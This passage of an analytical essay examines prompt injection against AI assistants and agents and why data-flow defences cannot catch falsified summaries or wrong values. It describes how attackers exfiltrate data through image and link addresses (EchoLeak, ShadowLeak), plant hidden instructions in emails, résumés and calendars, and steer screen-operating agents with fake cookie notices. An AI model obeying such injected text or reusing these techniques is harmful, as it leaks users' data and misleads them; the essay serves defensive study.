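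The researchers showed that real products followed such instructions, and Barracuda found criminals sending them. None of these reports documents anyone losing money or a password this way.

### Links that need a click and images that load by themselves

An injected answer can also carry the user's data to the attacker. When a program opens a web address, it sends most of that address to the site's owner. If an injection makes the model write a link to the attacker's site with the user's data in the address, opening the link sends that data to the attacker.

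*Trust No AI* (2024) describes a flaw of this kind that a researcher found in Microsoft 365 Copilot in February 2024. A phishing email made Copilot retrieve sensitive information from the user's inbox and hide it in a link using invisible characters. The information leaked only if the user clicked the link. Microsoft fixed the flaw that July.

Unlike a link, an image can leak data without a click, because a chat window that displays an image stored on another site requests it automatically, and the request includes the image's address. EchoLeak, another flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, relied on this behaviour. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, explain that an attacker only had to send an email. When the user later asked Copilot an unrelated work question, Copilot might read the email along with internal files and follow the email's hidden instructions. Its answer then included an image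 whose address contained private information, and the program displaying the answer sent that information out when it requested the image.

The security company Aim Security reported EchoLeak to Microsoft in January 2025. Microsoft fixed it in May, and both companies published the details in June. Microsoft said it knew of no exploitation against customers. Microsoft rated the flaw's severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026).

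Whether a data-flow defence would stop an attack like EchoLeak depends on what its designers count as an action. If they treat displaying an answer only as showing text to the user, the secrecy rule allows it, and the image then loads and sends the data out. But if they treat loading an image as a tool call that sends data to the image's host, the rule applies to the image's address. The address comes from private files and an outsider's email, so its label is {U, S}. The host is not a permitted reader of those files, so the system blocks the request. The system can check a link the same way before showing it.

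The table applies this rule to the different things an attacker might put in an answer.

| What the answer contains | What has to happen next | What the attacker gets | Would the secrecy rule stop it, if it covered display? |
|---|---|---|---|
| An image with private data in its address | Nothing | The data | Yes |
| A link with private data in its address | The user clicks | The data | Yes |
| An image with a fixed address | Nothing | Evidence that the user has seen the answer, and when | No |
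| A link to a false login page | The user clicks and types a password | The password | No |
| A phone number or a request to pay | The user calls or pays | Whatever the user reveals or sends | No |

In *ChatGPhish*, loading the fixed image sent the researchers' server the user's network address, browser type and the time at which ChatGPT produced the answer. Nothing in the image's address was secret, so a secrecy rule would not block it. A trust rule could, by refusing to load images from addresses that come from untrusted text. Permiso also had ChatGPT display a QR code that links to a web address. Scanning it moves the victim to their phone, away from the protections on their computer.

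In the last two rows, the user supplies the secret after the answer and outside the agent, so a rule about where the agent's data may go cannot protect it.

Data can also leave without anything appearing on the user's screen. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* also describes ShadowLeak, in which a hidden instruction in an email told ChatGPT's research agent to find sensitive data in the user's inbox and visit a web address containing that data. The request came from OpenAI's servers, so an employer monitoring its own computers might not detect it. OpenAI fixed the flaw in August 2025, and there was no known campaign against users. ShadowLeak is easier for a data-flow defence to handle than EchoLeak, because visiting a web page is already a tool call, which the policy checks.

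### Would people do what the answer tells them?

Andi Ahmeti, the Permiso researcher behind the Copilot tests, told Underhill that people have learned to distrust suspicious emails but do not apply this scepticism to AI summaries. This is plausible, but neither Permiso nor Figueroa showed the false alerts to ordinary users and counted how many clicked or called. Two large experiments on persuasion give some indirect evidence, though neither involved phishing.

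AI systems can be very persuasive in conversation. In *AI out-persuades expert humans in text-based dialogue* (Hackenburg, Wagner and colleagues, 2026), people discussed a British policy question by text with either an AI system or a human. The AI systems moved people's opinions 4.6 percentage points further than elite debaters did, who had chosen the topics and prepared for them. In another experiment, participants could give any part of a £1 bonus to Save the Children. Compared with a chat about something unrelated, a conversation with an AI system raised the average donation by about 21 pence, and one with a professional canvasser by about 7 pence.

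Much of this advantage would not carry over to a false alert in a summary, because an alert is only a few sentences long. The conversations typically lasted 14 minutes, and the AI systems wrote 294 words per reply on average, compared with 54 for the debaters. The AI systems seem to have won by making many more factual claims. When Hackenburg and colleagues limited an AI system to the length and speed of human replies, it did no better than debaters with extra coaching.

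Participants could hardly tell when they were being misled. The share of false claims in a conversation had almost no correlation (0.05) with their sense that their partner had lied or made things up. The effect on opinion had fallen from 12.9 percentage points to 1.9 when the researchers contacted participants again five to ten months later, but this is little protection against phishing, because a victim only has to believe the message for a few minutes.

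In *Eight weeks of stealth AI persuasion has little effect on political views*, Velez, Nikolovski and Kalla (2026) recruited 3,160 people to use a chatbot for everyday purposes. For eight weeks, one group's chatbot argued, unasked, against the user's view on universal basic income whenever the subject came up naturally. This moved support for the policy by about 1 percentage point, too little to distinguish from no effect. A single openly persuasive conversation moved it by 21 points.

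This result does not show that covert influence is harmless, because the chatbot had few chances to persuade people and never mentioned basic income to 40% of the covert group. In a separate test, Velez and colleagues paid participants to discuss social media with a chatbot secretly instructed to present social media favourably. Opinion moved by 0.17 standard deviations, about half the effect of the open conversation and five times that of the eight weeks of covert influence.

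An attacker with text in an email can reach the user more easily, because the alert appears in a summary the user requested. The alert's request is open, as in the persuasive conversation, but the person behind it is hidden, as in the covert one. The attacker also wants one quick action, whereas both research teams mainly measured opinions. So the experiments don't show how often people would obey a false alert.

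Velez and colleagues measured how much participants trusted their chatbot. After four weeks of regular use, average trust was 3.42 on a five-point scale, up from 3.27. Participants trusted the chatbot more than AI generally, but their trust fell short of the unquestioning trust that warnings about assistants sometimes assume.

### Asking the user to approve an action

The user's judgement matters even when the agent takes the action. When a tool call fails the policy, the system can refuse it or show an approval prompt asking the user whether to go ahead. Refusing every such call makes the agent less useful. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) note in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that strict policies reduced the rate of completed tasks on AgentDojo by up to 30%, even without an attack.

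Approval prompts can also cause user fatigue, which the CaMeL paper lists among the system's limits in a passage Willison quotes. Willison explains that people who face constant requests for approval tend to start saying yes to everything. He adds that tiredness can catch out even careful people, and mentions the security researcher Troy Hunt, who fell for a phishing attack in 2025 while jet-lagged. The anecdote is a reason for concern about approval prompts, but it is about phishing and doesn't show how quickly approval fatigue sets in.

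Kolluri and colleagues, most of them at Microsoft, tried to reduce the number of approval prompts. For each run of an agent, they count the tool calls that the policy would not allow without approval. They report the total number of such calls over all the tasks the agent completed, and TCR@k, the share of all tasks that the agent completed with at most k approvals each. If an agent completes three of four tasks, needing 0, 1 and 4 approvals, the total is 5, TCR@0 is 25% and TCR@1 is 50%.

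Prudentia, an agent built on FIDES, gives its planner model access to the labels and policies so that it can look for a plan that needs fewer approvals. This reduced the number of approvals on AgentDojo by a factor of up to 1.9. Prudentia needed no approvals on WASP, a second benchmark whose tasks never require the agent to choose its actions based on untrusted data.

Fewer prompts should mean less fatigue, and users may look more carefully at those that remain. But Kolluri and colleagues ran these measurements without attacks and assumed that the user would approve every call in a completed task. Their results show how often the agent would interrupt a user, but not whether the user would spot the one request that an attacker had caused.

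Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse an email, which changes the email's label from untrusted to trusted. Suppose the email contains a to-do list with ten items, each requiring an action that the policy would normally stop. The agent can ask for ten approvals or for a single endorsement. If the user endorses the email, the planner model reads the list and carries out all ten items without further approvals.

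Endorsing the email once saves nine interruptions, but more depends on that one answer. With separate prompts, the user could refuse a payment to a stranger and allow everything else. To endorse the email, they have to judge all of it before knowing what the agent will do with it, and it may contain hidden text that they can't see on the screen. If they endorse an email that contains an injection, the system treats the attacker's text as trusted, and the label no longer protects them.

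The information in an approval prompt matters as much as the number of prompts. If the model explains why an action is needed using untrusted text, the attacker can influence the prompt that was supposed to stop the attack. Software can avoid this by building the prompt from a fixed template that shows the recipient, the amount and where each value came from. Even then, users will interpret those details in light of what the assistant has already told them.

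Suppose the agent in the invoice example asks whether it may pay an account that isn't on the approved list. The request is accurate, but the employee has just read in the summary that the supplier changed banks, so they expect an unfamiliar account. Mascellino reports that Barracuda recommends human approval for payments and vendor changes. The approval would protect the company better if the employee first called the supplier on a number the company already had on file, because the attacker doesn't control that answer.

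## Why data-flow rules cannot tell a false answer from a true one

A data-flow rule limits what can be done with a piece of text based on where the text came from. A false summary of an email comes from the same email as a true one, so the rule applies equally to both. Better labels and stricter policies do not change this. Some designs limit how much of an answer an attacker can falsify, but each requires users to give up something they would like to have.

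### Two summaries with one label

Take the inbox with the bank's warning and the thief's email, and suppose the quarantined model summarises it twice. A model's output is partly random, so the model might ignore the thief's instruction the first time and write a faithful summary, s₁. The second time it obeys and writes s₂, which describes the bank's warning as routine. Costa and colleagues give a model's output the combined label of everything in its prompt. Leaving secrecy aside, the user's request is trusted and the emails are untrusted, so

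label(s₁) = { } ⊔ {U} = {U}

label(s₂) = { } ⊔ {U} = {U}

This calculation uses only the labels of the inputs, not the words of the summary. A rule based on labels must therefore allow both summaries or refuse both. Allowing both lets the false one reach the user, while refusing both means the user can't get a summary of outside email at all.

CaMeL's policies can depend on a value as well as its label. For example, a policy can compare an email address with a contact list. It cannot check a summary this way, because there is no list of correct summaries to compare it with.

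Another option is to require the answer to stay the same whatever an untrusted email contains. This kind of guarantee is called noninterference, and Costa and colleagues considered it too restrictive even for protecting secrets. It would make summarising untrusted emails impossible, because the answer would have to be the same whether the bank had written about a suspicious payment or its holiday opening hours.

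The user wants the email to influence the answer as information but not as an instruction. A label records only that the email influenced the answer, not how. Models don't reliably make this distinction either. Narisetty and colleagues cite measurements by Zverev and others in which models failed to keep instructions and data apart, and neither prompting nor further training reliably fixed this.

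Detecting a false summary therefore requires comparing it with the email. A summary is faithful if it gives a fair account of what the sender wrote and includes the parts that matter to the user, so judging it requires understanding both texts. If the user does this, they have read the email and no longer need the summary. A second model can save the user this work, but it also has to read the attacker's text, and Narisetty and colleagues point out that a guard model is as open to injection as any other model.

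A guard model may still help. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues accept that such filters make an attack harder, because the attacker has to get past two models, but they don't think filters can guarantee anything. Suppose an injection gets past each model 10% of the time. If the two models failed independently, it would get past both 1% of the time. If they always failed on the same emails, the figure would stay at 10%. The real figure is probably somewhere in between, since both models read the same text and a notice that gets past one may well get past the other.

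### What injection adds to an ordinary lie

One objection to worrying about this is that anyone who can send an email can already lie in it. If a criminal writes that a supplier has changed banks, even a faithful summary will report the change.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues rely on this kind of comparison several times. In one example, an agent asks a model whether each file in a folder is an invoice and sends the invoices to the accounts department. A malicious file can trick the model into answering yes, but the attacker could have got the same result by putting a real invoice in the folder.

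I think the comparison is sound only if the attacker can affect nothing but the description of their own document, and the reader knows whose document it is. Prompt injection can violate both conditions.

In an honest summary, the employee would read that the supplier says it has changed banks. An injected summary can instead list "update the supplier's bank details" as a task. The employee can doubt a claim attributed to the supplier, but the injected summary omits that attribution, so the claim appears to come from the assistant.

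Hidden text also lets the attacker keep the visible document truthful. Anyone who reads a visible lie might notice it, including colleagues who know the facts. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues mention résumés with instructions in tiny or white letters. A recruiter who opens such a file may see a modest, truthful résumé but not the hidden sentence that caused its high ranking.

An injection in one document can also change how a model treats other people's documents. One résumé injection they describe tells the model to ignore candidates who worked for a certain company. A recruiter who read that in a résumé would think it strange and carry on, but a model that reads all the résumés together may obey it. Similarly, the thief could always lie about himself, but he needed an injection to change what the user learned about the bank's email.

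Finally, a lie only adds a claim, so someone reading the inbox themselves would see the bank's warning as well as the thief's message. An injection can make the assistant leave the warning out of its summary.

The objection still gives designers a realistic target, which is to limit the attacker to what they could achieve by lying openly under their own name. Users would then be about as safe as they would be reading their own mail, though the summary could still be false.

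### One model call for each email

Suppose a user has 20 new emails, one of them hostile, and asks for a one-line summary of each. In the simplest design, the quarantined model reads all 20 emails in one prompt, so each email can influence all 20 summaries. Of these 400 possible influences, the user wants only the 20 in which an email affects its own summary. The other 380 are ways for one sender to change the summary of another sender's email.

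The alternative is to call the model 20 times, with one email in each prompt, and have ordinary software put the lines in a list. The hostile email is then in only one prompt, so it can falsify only one line, even if the model follows every injection in its prompts.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues call this the map-reduce pattern, after a method for spreading large computations across many machines. The "map" step processes each document separately, and the "reduce" step combines the results.

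The combining step can undo the protection. If another model reads the 20 lines and summarises them, the hostile line may contain an injection aimed at that model. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues allow two safe versions. Either the combining step uses no model and tolerates a bad value from any one document, or software restricts the results of the map step to a format that can't carry an instruction, such as a number.

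| Design | What one hostile email among 20 can change |
|---|---|
| One call reads all the emails | Any of the lines, or all of them |
| One call per email, and software lists the lines | Its own line |
| One call per email, and another model writes an overview of the lines | Possibly the whole overview |
| One call per email gives an urgency score, and software shows the top three | Its own score, which can push one honest email off the list |

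In the last row, an attacker can still suppress some emails, because three hostile emails with the highest score would fill the whole list. The attacker could try this without injection by writing three emails that sound urgent, so this is close to the target. A link to the other 17 emails would help, because the user would at least know that the list is incomplete.

Twenty separate calls cost more than one, but perhaps not 20 times as much, because the model reads each email once in either design and only the instructions are repeated. The calls can also run at the same time.

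The more serious drawback is that no model processes two emails together. If one colleague moves a meeting to Thursday and another later moves it to Friday, a model given both emails can produce a summary that puts the meeting on Friday. With separate calls, the user gets two lines and has to work out the day. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give "What is the current status of Project A?" as an example request for an email assistant, with a paragraph drawn from several emails as the answer. That answer depends on connecting information across emails, which separate calls prevent.

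The designer also has to decide what counts as one source. When a colleague replies to an attacker and leaves the attacker's message quoted underneath, the reply contains text by both of them. Giving the reply its own model call protects the other 19 emails, but the attacker's text can still affect how the model reads the colleague's words.

### Answers from a fixed list

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a product recommender in which a shopper names a category, such as toasters, and a model reads the reviews in an online store and describes each product's advantages and drawbacks. The model can't buy anything or take any other consequential action, so a policy that checks such actions never applies. A hostile review can still contain an instruction to recommend a different product.

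Their safest design gives each review its own model call and allows only fixed categories as output, such as "good price" or "easy to use". Software then counts the results. If 120 of 200 reviews call a toaster easy to use, one more review can raise the share only from 60.0% to 60.2%, however it is worded. An ordinary positive review could have the same effect. A hundred fake reviews would raise the share to 73.3%, but fake reviews were already a problem for online stores before they used language models.

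The drawback is that someone has to think of the categories. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that shoppers who don't know the product may miss important ones, and suggest having the model propose some first. I think fixed categories also handle unexpected information badly. If four reviewers report that the toaster caught fire and no category covers safety, the design discards the most important fact in the reviews, even with no attacker involved.

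FIDES ranks the formats it records in its labels by how much information they can carry. A yes or no carries one bit, a choice among eight options carries three, and free text has no limit.

An answer of only a few bits can still have a large effect. "Does this email need action today?" takes one bit to answer, and a false "no" about the bank's warning could cost the user money. In the security-log study, a fixed template only reduced the success rate of one attack from 96% to 38%.

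How the software combines yes-or-no answers can determine which mistakes an attacker can cause. Suppose the user asks whether any of the 20 emails needs action. If one model reads them all, the hostile email may force a "no". If the model answers for each email separately and the software reports "yes" when at least one answer is yes, the hostile email can cause a false alarm but can't cancel a "yes" for the bank's email. For this question, a false alarm is usually better than a missed email.

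### Ranking and comparing résumés

Hiring is harder because a recruiter wants to compare candidates, not just count categories. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues examine several designs for an assistant that screens résumés.

In one résumé-screening design, no model reads the raw résumés. Software measures how similar each résumé is to queries based on the job requirements and returns the closest matches. Candidates can still improve their own rank by choosing the right words, but they can't give instructions about anyone else. The recruiter gets a list without explanations. If a model then summarises the top ten together, injections work again, and a hostile candidate can get into the top ten by matching their résumé to the public job advertisement.

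To get explanations safely, they suggest having the planner model write a sentence with gaps, such as "Candidate X is the best because they have Y more years of experience than the others", before any model reads the résumés. The planner also writes a small program to calculate the missing values. A quarantined model then reads each résumé separately and returns only the number of years.

If three candidates have 12, 9 and 3 years of experience and the third hides an instruction to report 30, the program subtracts the next highest figure, 12. The recruiter then reads that this candidate has 18 more years of experience than the others. The candidate wins the comparison with a false number, but the instruction cannot change the other candidates' figures, add a remark about them or alter the wording of the sentence.

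A candidate could also have printed "30 years" openly, so this is nearly an ordinary lie, except that the visible résumé still shows 3. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest pointing the recruiter to the passage behind each value so that they can check it. They also warn that the design depends on a good template, which may take the user considerable effort to get. It is much easier to write a template with a blank for "years of experience" than one for "would work well with this team".

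### Quotations and origins

Software can check whether a quotation is exact by searching the source for the same sequence of characters, but it can't check whether a summary is fair. Quotation is therefore one of the few ways to give users readable text with a property that a program can verify.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the idea to a chatbot that answers questions about medicines from their leaflets. Their threat model is the reverse of the one for email. They trust the leaflets, since the industry is heavily regulated, and the attacker is a user trying to make the chatbot give an illegal answer. For example, answering "no" when asked whether a drug causes nausea would be a problem if the leaflet gives a slight chance of it. In their design, the model finds the relevant parts of the leaflet and the program displays only those parts.

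The user then can't make the chatbot display an invented statement, but may still get the model to leave out a relevant passage. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of contraindications, the conditions under which a patient should not take the drug.

An exact quotation from an email can also mislead. If the bank wrote "No action is needed if you made this payment yourself", a program that checks quotations against the message could approve "No action is needed". Requiring whole sentences would prevent this, but a model that reads the whole inbox together could still follow the thief's instruction to quote only the bank's polite closing line. Quotation therefore works best when the model reads each email in a separate call, which keeps the thief's instruction away from the bank's email. Even then, a page of extracts is much less convenient than a summary because it takes longer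 to read.

Showing where each sentence came from deals with a different part of the problem, the loss of the sender's name. One way to do this is to ask the model to cite its sources, but the model writes the citations after reading the attacker's text, so an injection can influence them too. A more trustworthy way is to use the record that CaMeL or FIDES already keeps, because the quarantined model can't rewrite it.

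On its own, the record of sources is often too coarse to be useful. If one call reads all 20 emails, every sentence of the answer has all 20 as its sources. With a separate call for each email, each line has only one source, and the program can print the sender's address beside it. The supplier's alleged change of bank then appears next to a stranger's address. The program should print the address where the summary's text can't appear, or an attacker could add a false sender to the summary.

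Costa and colleagues mention a method from Siddiqui and others that gives more precise labels without separating everything in advance. It analyses which inputs influenced a response, then has the model rewrite the response from those inputs alone, so the new label covers only them. This might preserve more connections between emails, but the method would presumably keep a hostile email that influenced the response.

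Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that showing origins also makes work for shoppers, who would have to read the cited reviews and perhaps count them, because one advantage may come from a single review and another from dozens. Citations are also more useful for checking why a product is on the list than why another is missing. If a hostile review has discredited a competitor, the shopper may see nothing to check.

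### Links and invisible text

If the model receives only the text that the recipient would see, as Gibney advises, an attacker has to put any instruction where the recipient might notice it. The filter needs to cover white letters, tiny type and the invisible characters that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues mention. Those characters can carry hidden instructions into a model, or carry private data out in an email the user has approved.

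Outgoing links need to be checked because they can send data from the conversation to a third party. Blockchain News describes an OpenAI mechanism called Safe Url that looks for such links. It either shows the user exactly what the link would send and requires confirmation, or blocks it. This is more informative than a general warning, but it adds another approval prompt, and users may tire of reading them. Removing every link would avoid the prompts but also remove the meeting links and tracking pages that people often want from their email.

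Neither measure checks what the remaining text means, so a visible sentence addressed to the assistant still gets through.

### Training and detectors

All the measures so far assume that the model may obey the attacker. Developers also try to make this less likely by training models to ignore injected instructions and by running detectors for them. These methods did poorly at first. Narisetty and colleagues report that in 2025 Nasr and others tested twelve published defences, most of which had originally been reported to have attack success rates near zero. The tests used adaptive attacks, which are designed with knowledge of the defence, and these succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve. Human testers reached a 100% success rate.

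A detector's good benchmark score could be misleading. Narisetty and colleagues describe Attention Tracker, which separated attacks from harmless text perfectly on standard benchmarks but missed 69% of the attacks in another set. A simple adaptive attack that used only separator tokens raised the miss rate to 100%.

The coding-task figures for Claude Opus 4.5 also belong to this earlier period. Attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt and 63.0% with a hundred. If every attempt had an independent 4.7% chance of success, at least one of a hundred attempts would have succeeded 1 − 0.953¹⁰⁰ ≈ 99% of the time. The measured 63.0% suggests that the attacks differed in difficulty, and that some kept failing however often the attacker tried.

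Models improved a great deal during 2026. The figures below come from the developers' own documents, as reported by VentureBeat, ThreatCluster's *Claude Opus 5 Achieves 2% Success Rate Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* and TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026). "Safeguards" are protections the developer adds around the model.

| Model | Test | Attack success rate | Reported by |
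|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 (February 2026) | Coding, 200 attempts | 0% without safeguards | VentureBeat |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Operating a graphical interface, one attempt | 17.8% without safeguards | VentureBeat |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | The same, 200 attempts | 78.6% without safeguards, 57.1% with them | VentureBeat |
| Claude Opus 4.8 (May 2026) | Browser agent, per attempt | 31.5% without safeguards, 0.5% with them | VentureBeat |
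| Claude Opus 5 (July 2026) | Benchmark by the security company Gray Swan, 15 attempts | 2%, compared with 5.5% for Opus 4.8 | ThreatCluster |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (August 2026) | Instructions in outside content, average | 3.77% | TechRepublic |

The rows come from different tests, so they don't form a ranking. Opus 4.8 appears twice, with 31.5% in a browser and 5.5% on Gray Swan's benchmark, which shows how much the result depends on the setting. The browser figure also depends heavily on the safeguards, so it is of little use to a developer who uses the same model without them.

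OpenAI's numbers also vary with how the attack reaches the model. Direct attacks, in which the user types the malicious instruction, succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol only about 0.05% of the time. The 3.77% rate is for instructions in material that the model receives through a tool, which is the relevant kind of attack for email summaries. TechRepublic notes that these are shares of test attempts, not the probability of a real breach. But even a success rate of a few per cent is useful to a criminal, because sending the same email to thousands of people costs very little.

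Part of the improvement comes from training against better attackers. OpenAI built a model, GPT-Red, to find injections that work. OpenAI's earlier models were highly vulnerable to these attacks, which the company used to train GPT-5.6. OpenAI also reports that its latest models had already reached the ceiling of commonly used robustness tests, so a near-perfect score on one of those tests may mean only that the test has become too easy.

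Both companies have since released newer models. OpenAI describes GPT-6 Astra as significantly more robust than GPT-5.6 Sol to jailbreaks, which are attempts by users to get around a model's rules. That is encouraging, but it doesn't measure how the model handles a hostile email.

A public challenge in 2026 did use email. Anyone could write to an assistant running on Claude Opus 4.6 and try to extract a secret it held (Willison, 2026). Nobody succeeded in 6,000 attempts. If the attempts had been independent, this would put the success rate for that kind of attack below about 0.05%, with 95% confidence. Willison takes this as a sign that the model's training has made these attacks much harder.

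However, it was a test of leaks. The assistant's instructions prohibited it from revealing credentials, changing its own files, running commands or sending data out because of something in an email. They did not require it to keep one sender's email from changing how it described another's, and participants could win without causing such a change.

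## Wrong values inside permitted actions

A false summary misleads the user, but an agent can also send false text to someone else, and the user may never see it. This can happen in the example from Beurer-Kellner and colleagues about sending today's schedule to the user's boss, John Doe. In an agent like CaMeL, the plan would look roughly like this:

```
events = read_calendar("today")
text   = ask_quarantined("Write this up as a short email", events)
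send_email(recipient="john.doe@company.com", body=text)
```

The recipient is fixed, but the message body has to come from the calendar, where anyone who can send the user a meeting invitation may be able to add text. A hostile entry can make the quarantined model write that the user is taking the afternoon off, or include a link and ask the boss to log in. An honest schedule would also be labelled untrusted, so a usable policy has to allow untrusted text in the body.

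The attacker may not need an instruction. *SPA* (2026), which presents a defence for agents that work across several requests, points out that a plan can run exactly as the user intended and still transfer money to an attacker's bank account. An invitation to a fake meeting is enough to falsify the schedule. Training a model to ignore planted instructions doesn't help here, because the attacker hasn't planted any.

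As with email summaries, the damage is smaller if ordinary software lists the calendar entries one by one, because a hostile entry can then affect only its own line.

### Which arguments a rule can check

A rule can catch a wrong value if it can compare the value with a source the attacker doesn't control. For example, it can check John Doe's address against the user's request or contact list.

Amounts are harder to protect. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) gives an example in which a user asks the agent to send a colleague half the cost of a team dinner. The agent chooses the right tool and colleague, but a planted "Correction" entry gives a false total. If the dinner cost $120 and the entry lists $1,200, the colleague receives $600 instead of $60. A $100 cap on such payments would stop this, but it would let through the $95 payment that results from a false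 total of $190. Taking the total only from the bank's own amount field would be safer, if the bank provides one that outsiders can't write to.

Ameur, Mendes and Bouzefrane (2026), in *Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, measured how much the type of argument matters. Their system, IntentFlow, compares each proposed tool call with a list of what the user authorised and checks where the values came from. They tested it on 200 simulated attacks against an agent that could send emails, create calendar events, write files and query databases.

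| What the attack changed | Attacks | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Recipient, attachment, participant, file path or database address | 134 | 0 |
| Database query | 34 | 0 |
| Date of an event | 8 | 0 |
| Subject of an email | 8 | 8 |
| Description of an event | 8 | 8 |
| Contents of a file | 8 | 8 |

The overall success rate was 12%, but Ameur and colleagues acknowledge that this depends on the mix of attacks. Attacks on content fields, including dates, succeeded 75% of the time. If these attacks had made up half the test instead of 16%, the overall rate would have been 37.5%.

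The zeros are also a best case, because the benchmark gave IntentFlow a correct list of the user's authorisations and identified which documents contained injections and which arguments were sensitive. When software inferred which of 150 arguments from other tools were sensitive, it missed about 26% of the sensitive ones.

*ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) reports a similar pattern with a different defence. ROPE gives each sensitive argument a rule about its origin. A rule may require the value to appear in the user's request, or in an authenticated message from someone the request names. When the user has asked the agent to compose an email, the rule for its wording is called FREE and accepts anything.

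Across two benchmarks and several models, 51 attacks succeeded against ROPE. In 23 of them the harm was in the agent's reply to the user, which ROPE doesn't check. Another 21 put harmful content into an action with a permitted destination. In one of these, the user asked the agent to summarise an article and send the summary to a colleague, Alice. The article contained an instruction to send Alice a link, so the agent sent her the link and then the summary. ROPE allowed both messages because the user had named Alice.

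In the remaining seven cases, the user's request left a sensitive value to be filled in entirely from material that an attacker could write. A stricter rule would stop this, but it would also block some honest requests. Ma and colleagues describe a user who asks the agent to fetch and pay an electricity bill. The supplier's account number appears only in the bill, so ROPE refuses the payment, because it can't tell from the number's origin whether a criminal has replaced it. In tests without attacks, 96 of the 411 tasks failed after ROPE had refused a tool call, and 83 of those failed for this kind of reason.

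### Trusted values that the user didn't choose

A value can be wrong even if it comes from a trusted source. In an example from Ameur and colleagues, the user asks the agent to send a quarterly summary to "my manager", and the agent picks the legal team's address from the company directory. The directory is trusted, so a check based only on a value's origin allows the email. An outdated directory or an old email thread can cause the same error without an attacker.

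The researchers built 50 such cases. A check based only on origins let all 50 through, while IntentFlow stopped all of them and allowed all 50 corresponding legitimate tasks. A simplified imitation of CaMeL's check also stopped every wrong value, but refused 16 of the legitimate tasks because it required the exact value to appear in the request. A request that says "my manager", for example, doesn't contain the manager's email address. IntentFlow looks up such phrases in a directory that somebody has to compile by hand and keep up to date.

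### Why a click is hard to check

A tool called `send_email` has a clear purpose and a separate argument for the recipient. An agent that operates a computer through its screen instead has tools like `click(412, 630)`, where the numbers are screen coordinates. As Foerster and colleagues explain, the same click could log the user in, delete data or open a malicious website, depending on what is at those coordinates.

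A CaMeL policy for this tool would receive the tool's name, the two numbers that give the click position, and their labels. The numbers are untrusted because they come from the quarantined model's reading of the screen. A policy that refused untrusted positions would stop the agent from clicking on anything it had found on the screen, while one that accepted them would allow clicks on any button.

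Foerster and colleagues therefore left security policies out of CaMeL-NOVA, their adaptation of CaMeL to these agents, and they describe the design as a worst-case baseline.

Because the planner model can't see the screen, the plan also needs a branch for each state the agent might find. If the user wants this month's weather forecast for Manchester, the browser might be closed, or it might be open with a cookie notice covering the page. With simplified function names, the part for cookie notices might look like this:

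```
screen = describe_screen("Is anything covering the page?")
if matches(screen, "a cookie notice is visible"):
    button = find("the button that accepts cookies")
    click(button)
```

The quarantined model describes the screen. Another isolated model call compares the description with the expected state, and the interpreter uses the result to decide whether to enter a branch of the program. Inside the branch, the quarantined model supplies the position of the button to click. The quarantined model can't add a line to the program, but a false report from it can make the agent enter the wrong branch or click in the wrong place.

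Plans for desktop tasks can have many branches that depend on a model's output. On OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in ordinary desktop programs, CaMeL-NOVA's plans had an average of 39.7 branches, and 24.2 of them depended on a model's output. On AgentDojo, where the tools have names like `send_email`, CaMeL's plans had an average of 3.7 branches, and 1.9 of them depended on a model's output.

### Steering an agent through its own plan

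Foerster and colleagues demonstrated two branch steering attacks. In one, the fake cookie notice leads the agent to the attacker's site. The attacker doesn't need to know much about the user's task, because almost any plan for browsing the web includes dealing with cookie notices. The agent also searches for a notice the same way at every point in the plan, so it doesn't check whether a notice makes sense on that page.

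The other attack makes small changes to the pixels of an advertisement, which cause the quarantined model to misread the rest of the page. On a website about medicines, the user wanted the natural products database, but the model chose the link to a particular drug and gave the plausible reason that the drug was a natural product. A company could use this attack to bring more visitors to its products.

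The fixed plan still limits what such attacks can do. An attacker can send the agent to another site with one false report, but can steal money only if the user's task already includes a payment and the agent is logged in at the right moment. Foerster and colleagues estimate that theft would also require at least two false reports that fit together, such as one about the recipient field and one about the confirmation button. A request for a weather forecast is therefore much less dangerous than a request to pay an invoice.

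They also tried to catch false reports by having other models check them. In one check, a second model receives the page's underlying structure and judges whether the proposed click matches what the plan was looking for. A stronger version adds a third model, from a different developer, that examines the screenshot.

| Check | Fake cookie notices caught | Legitimate tasks wrongly stopped |
|---|---|---|
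| Page structure | 6 of 10 | 4 of 17 |
| Page structure and screenshot | 5 of 10 | 3 of 17 |

The rows don't show which check is better, because the stronger check was tested against a harder attack. In that attack, the advertiser could supply the banner's code, which removed the "Advertisement" marking from the page structure. The samples are also very small. Still, both checks missed about half of the attacks. They also stopped roughly a fifth of the legitimate tasks, nearly always because they mistook a real cookie notice for a fake one. The pixel attack got past the stronger check even when the researchers tuned the check to favour security and accepted many false alarms.

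### How much work CaMeL-NOVA can still do

Foerster and colleagues report that CaMeL-NOVA keeps up to 57% of the performance of frontier models on OSWorld. They tested it on the 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had solved on its own with a limit of 15 steps. With Claude as its quarantined model, CaMeL-NOVA solved 31 of these tasks (28%) on the first attempt and 62 (57%) within five attempts. The higher figure assumes that somebody can recognise the successful attempt, which is easy on a benchmark with automatic scoring but harder in an office, where a failed attempt may already have changed something.

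The reported gain for small models also depends on the number of attempts. UI-TARS, a small model trained to operate computers, scored 24.4% on its own with one attempt and 29.0% within CaMeL-NOVA with up to three. If only the first attempt counts, its score within CaMeL-NOVA is about 22%, slightly below its score without the defence.

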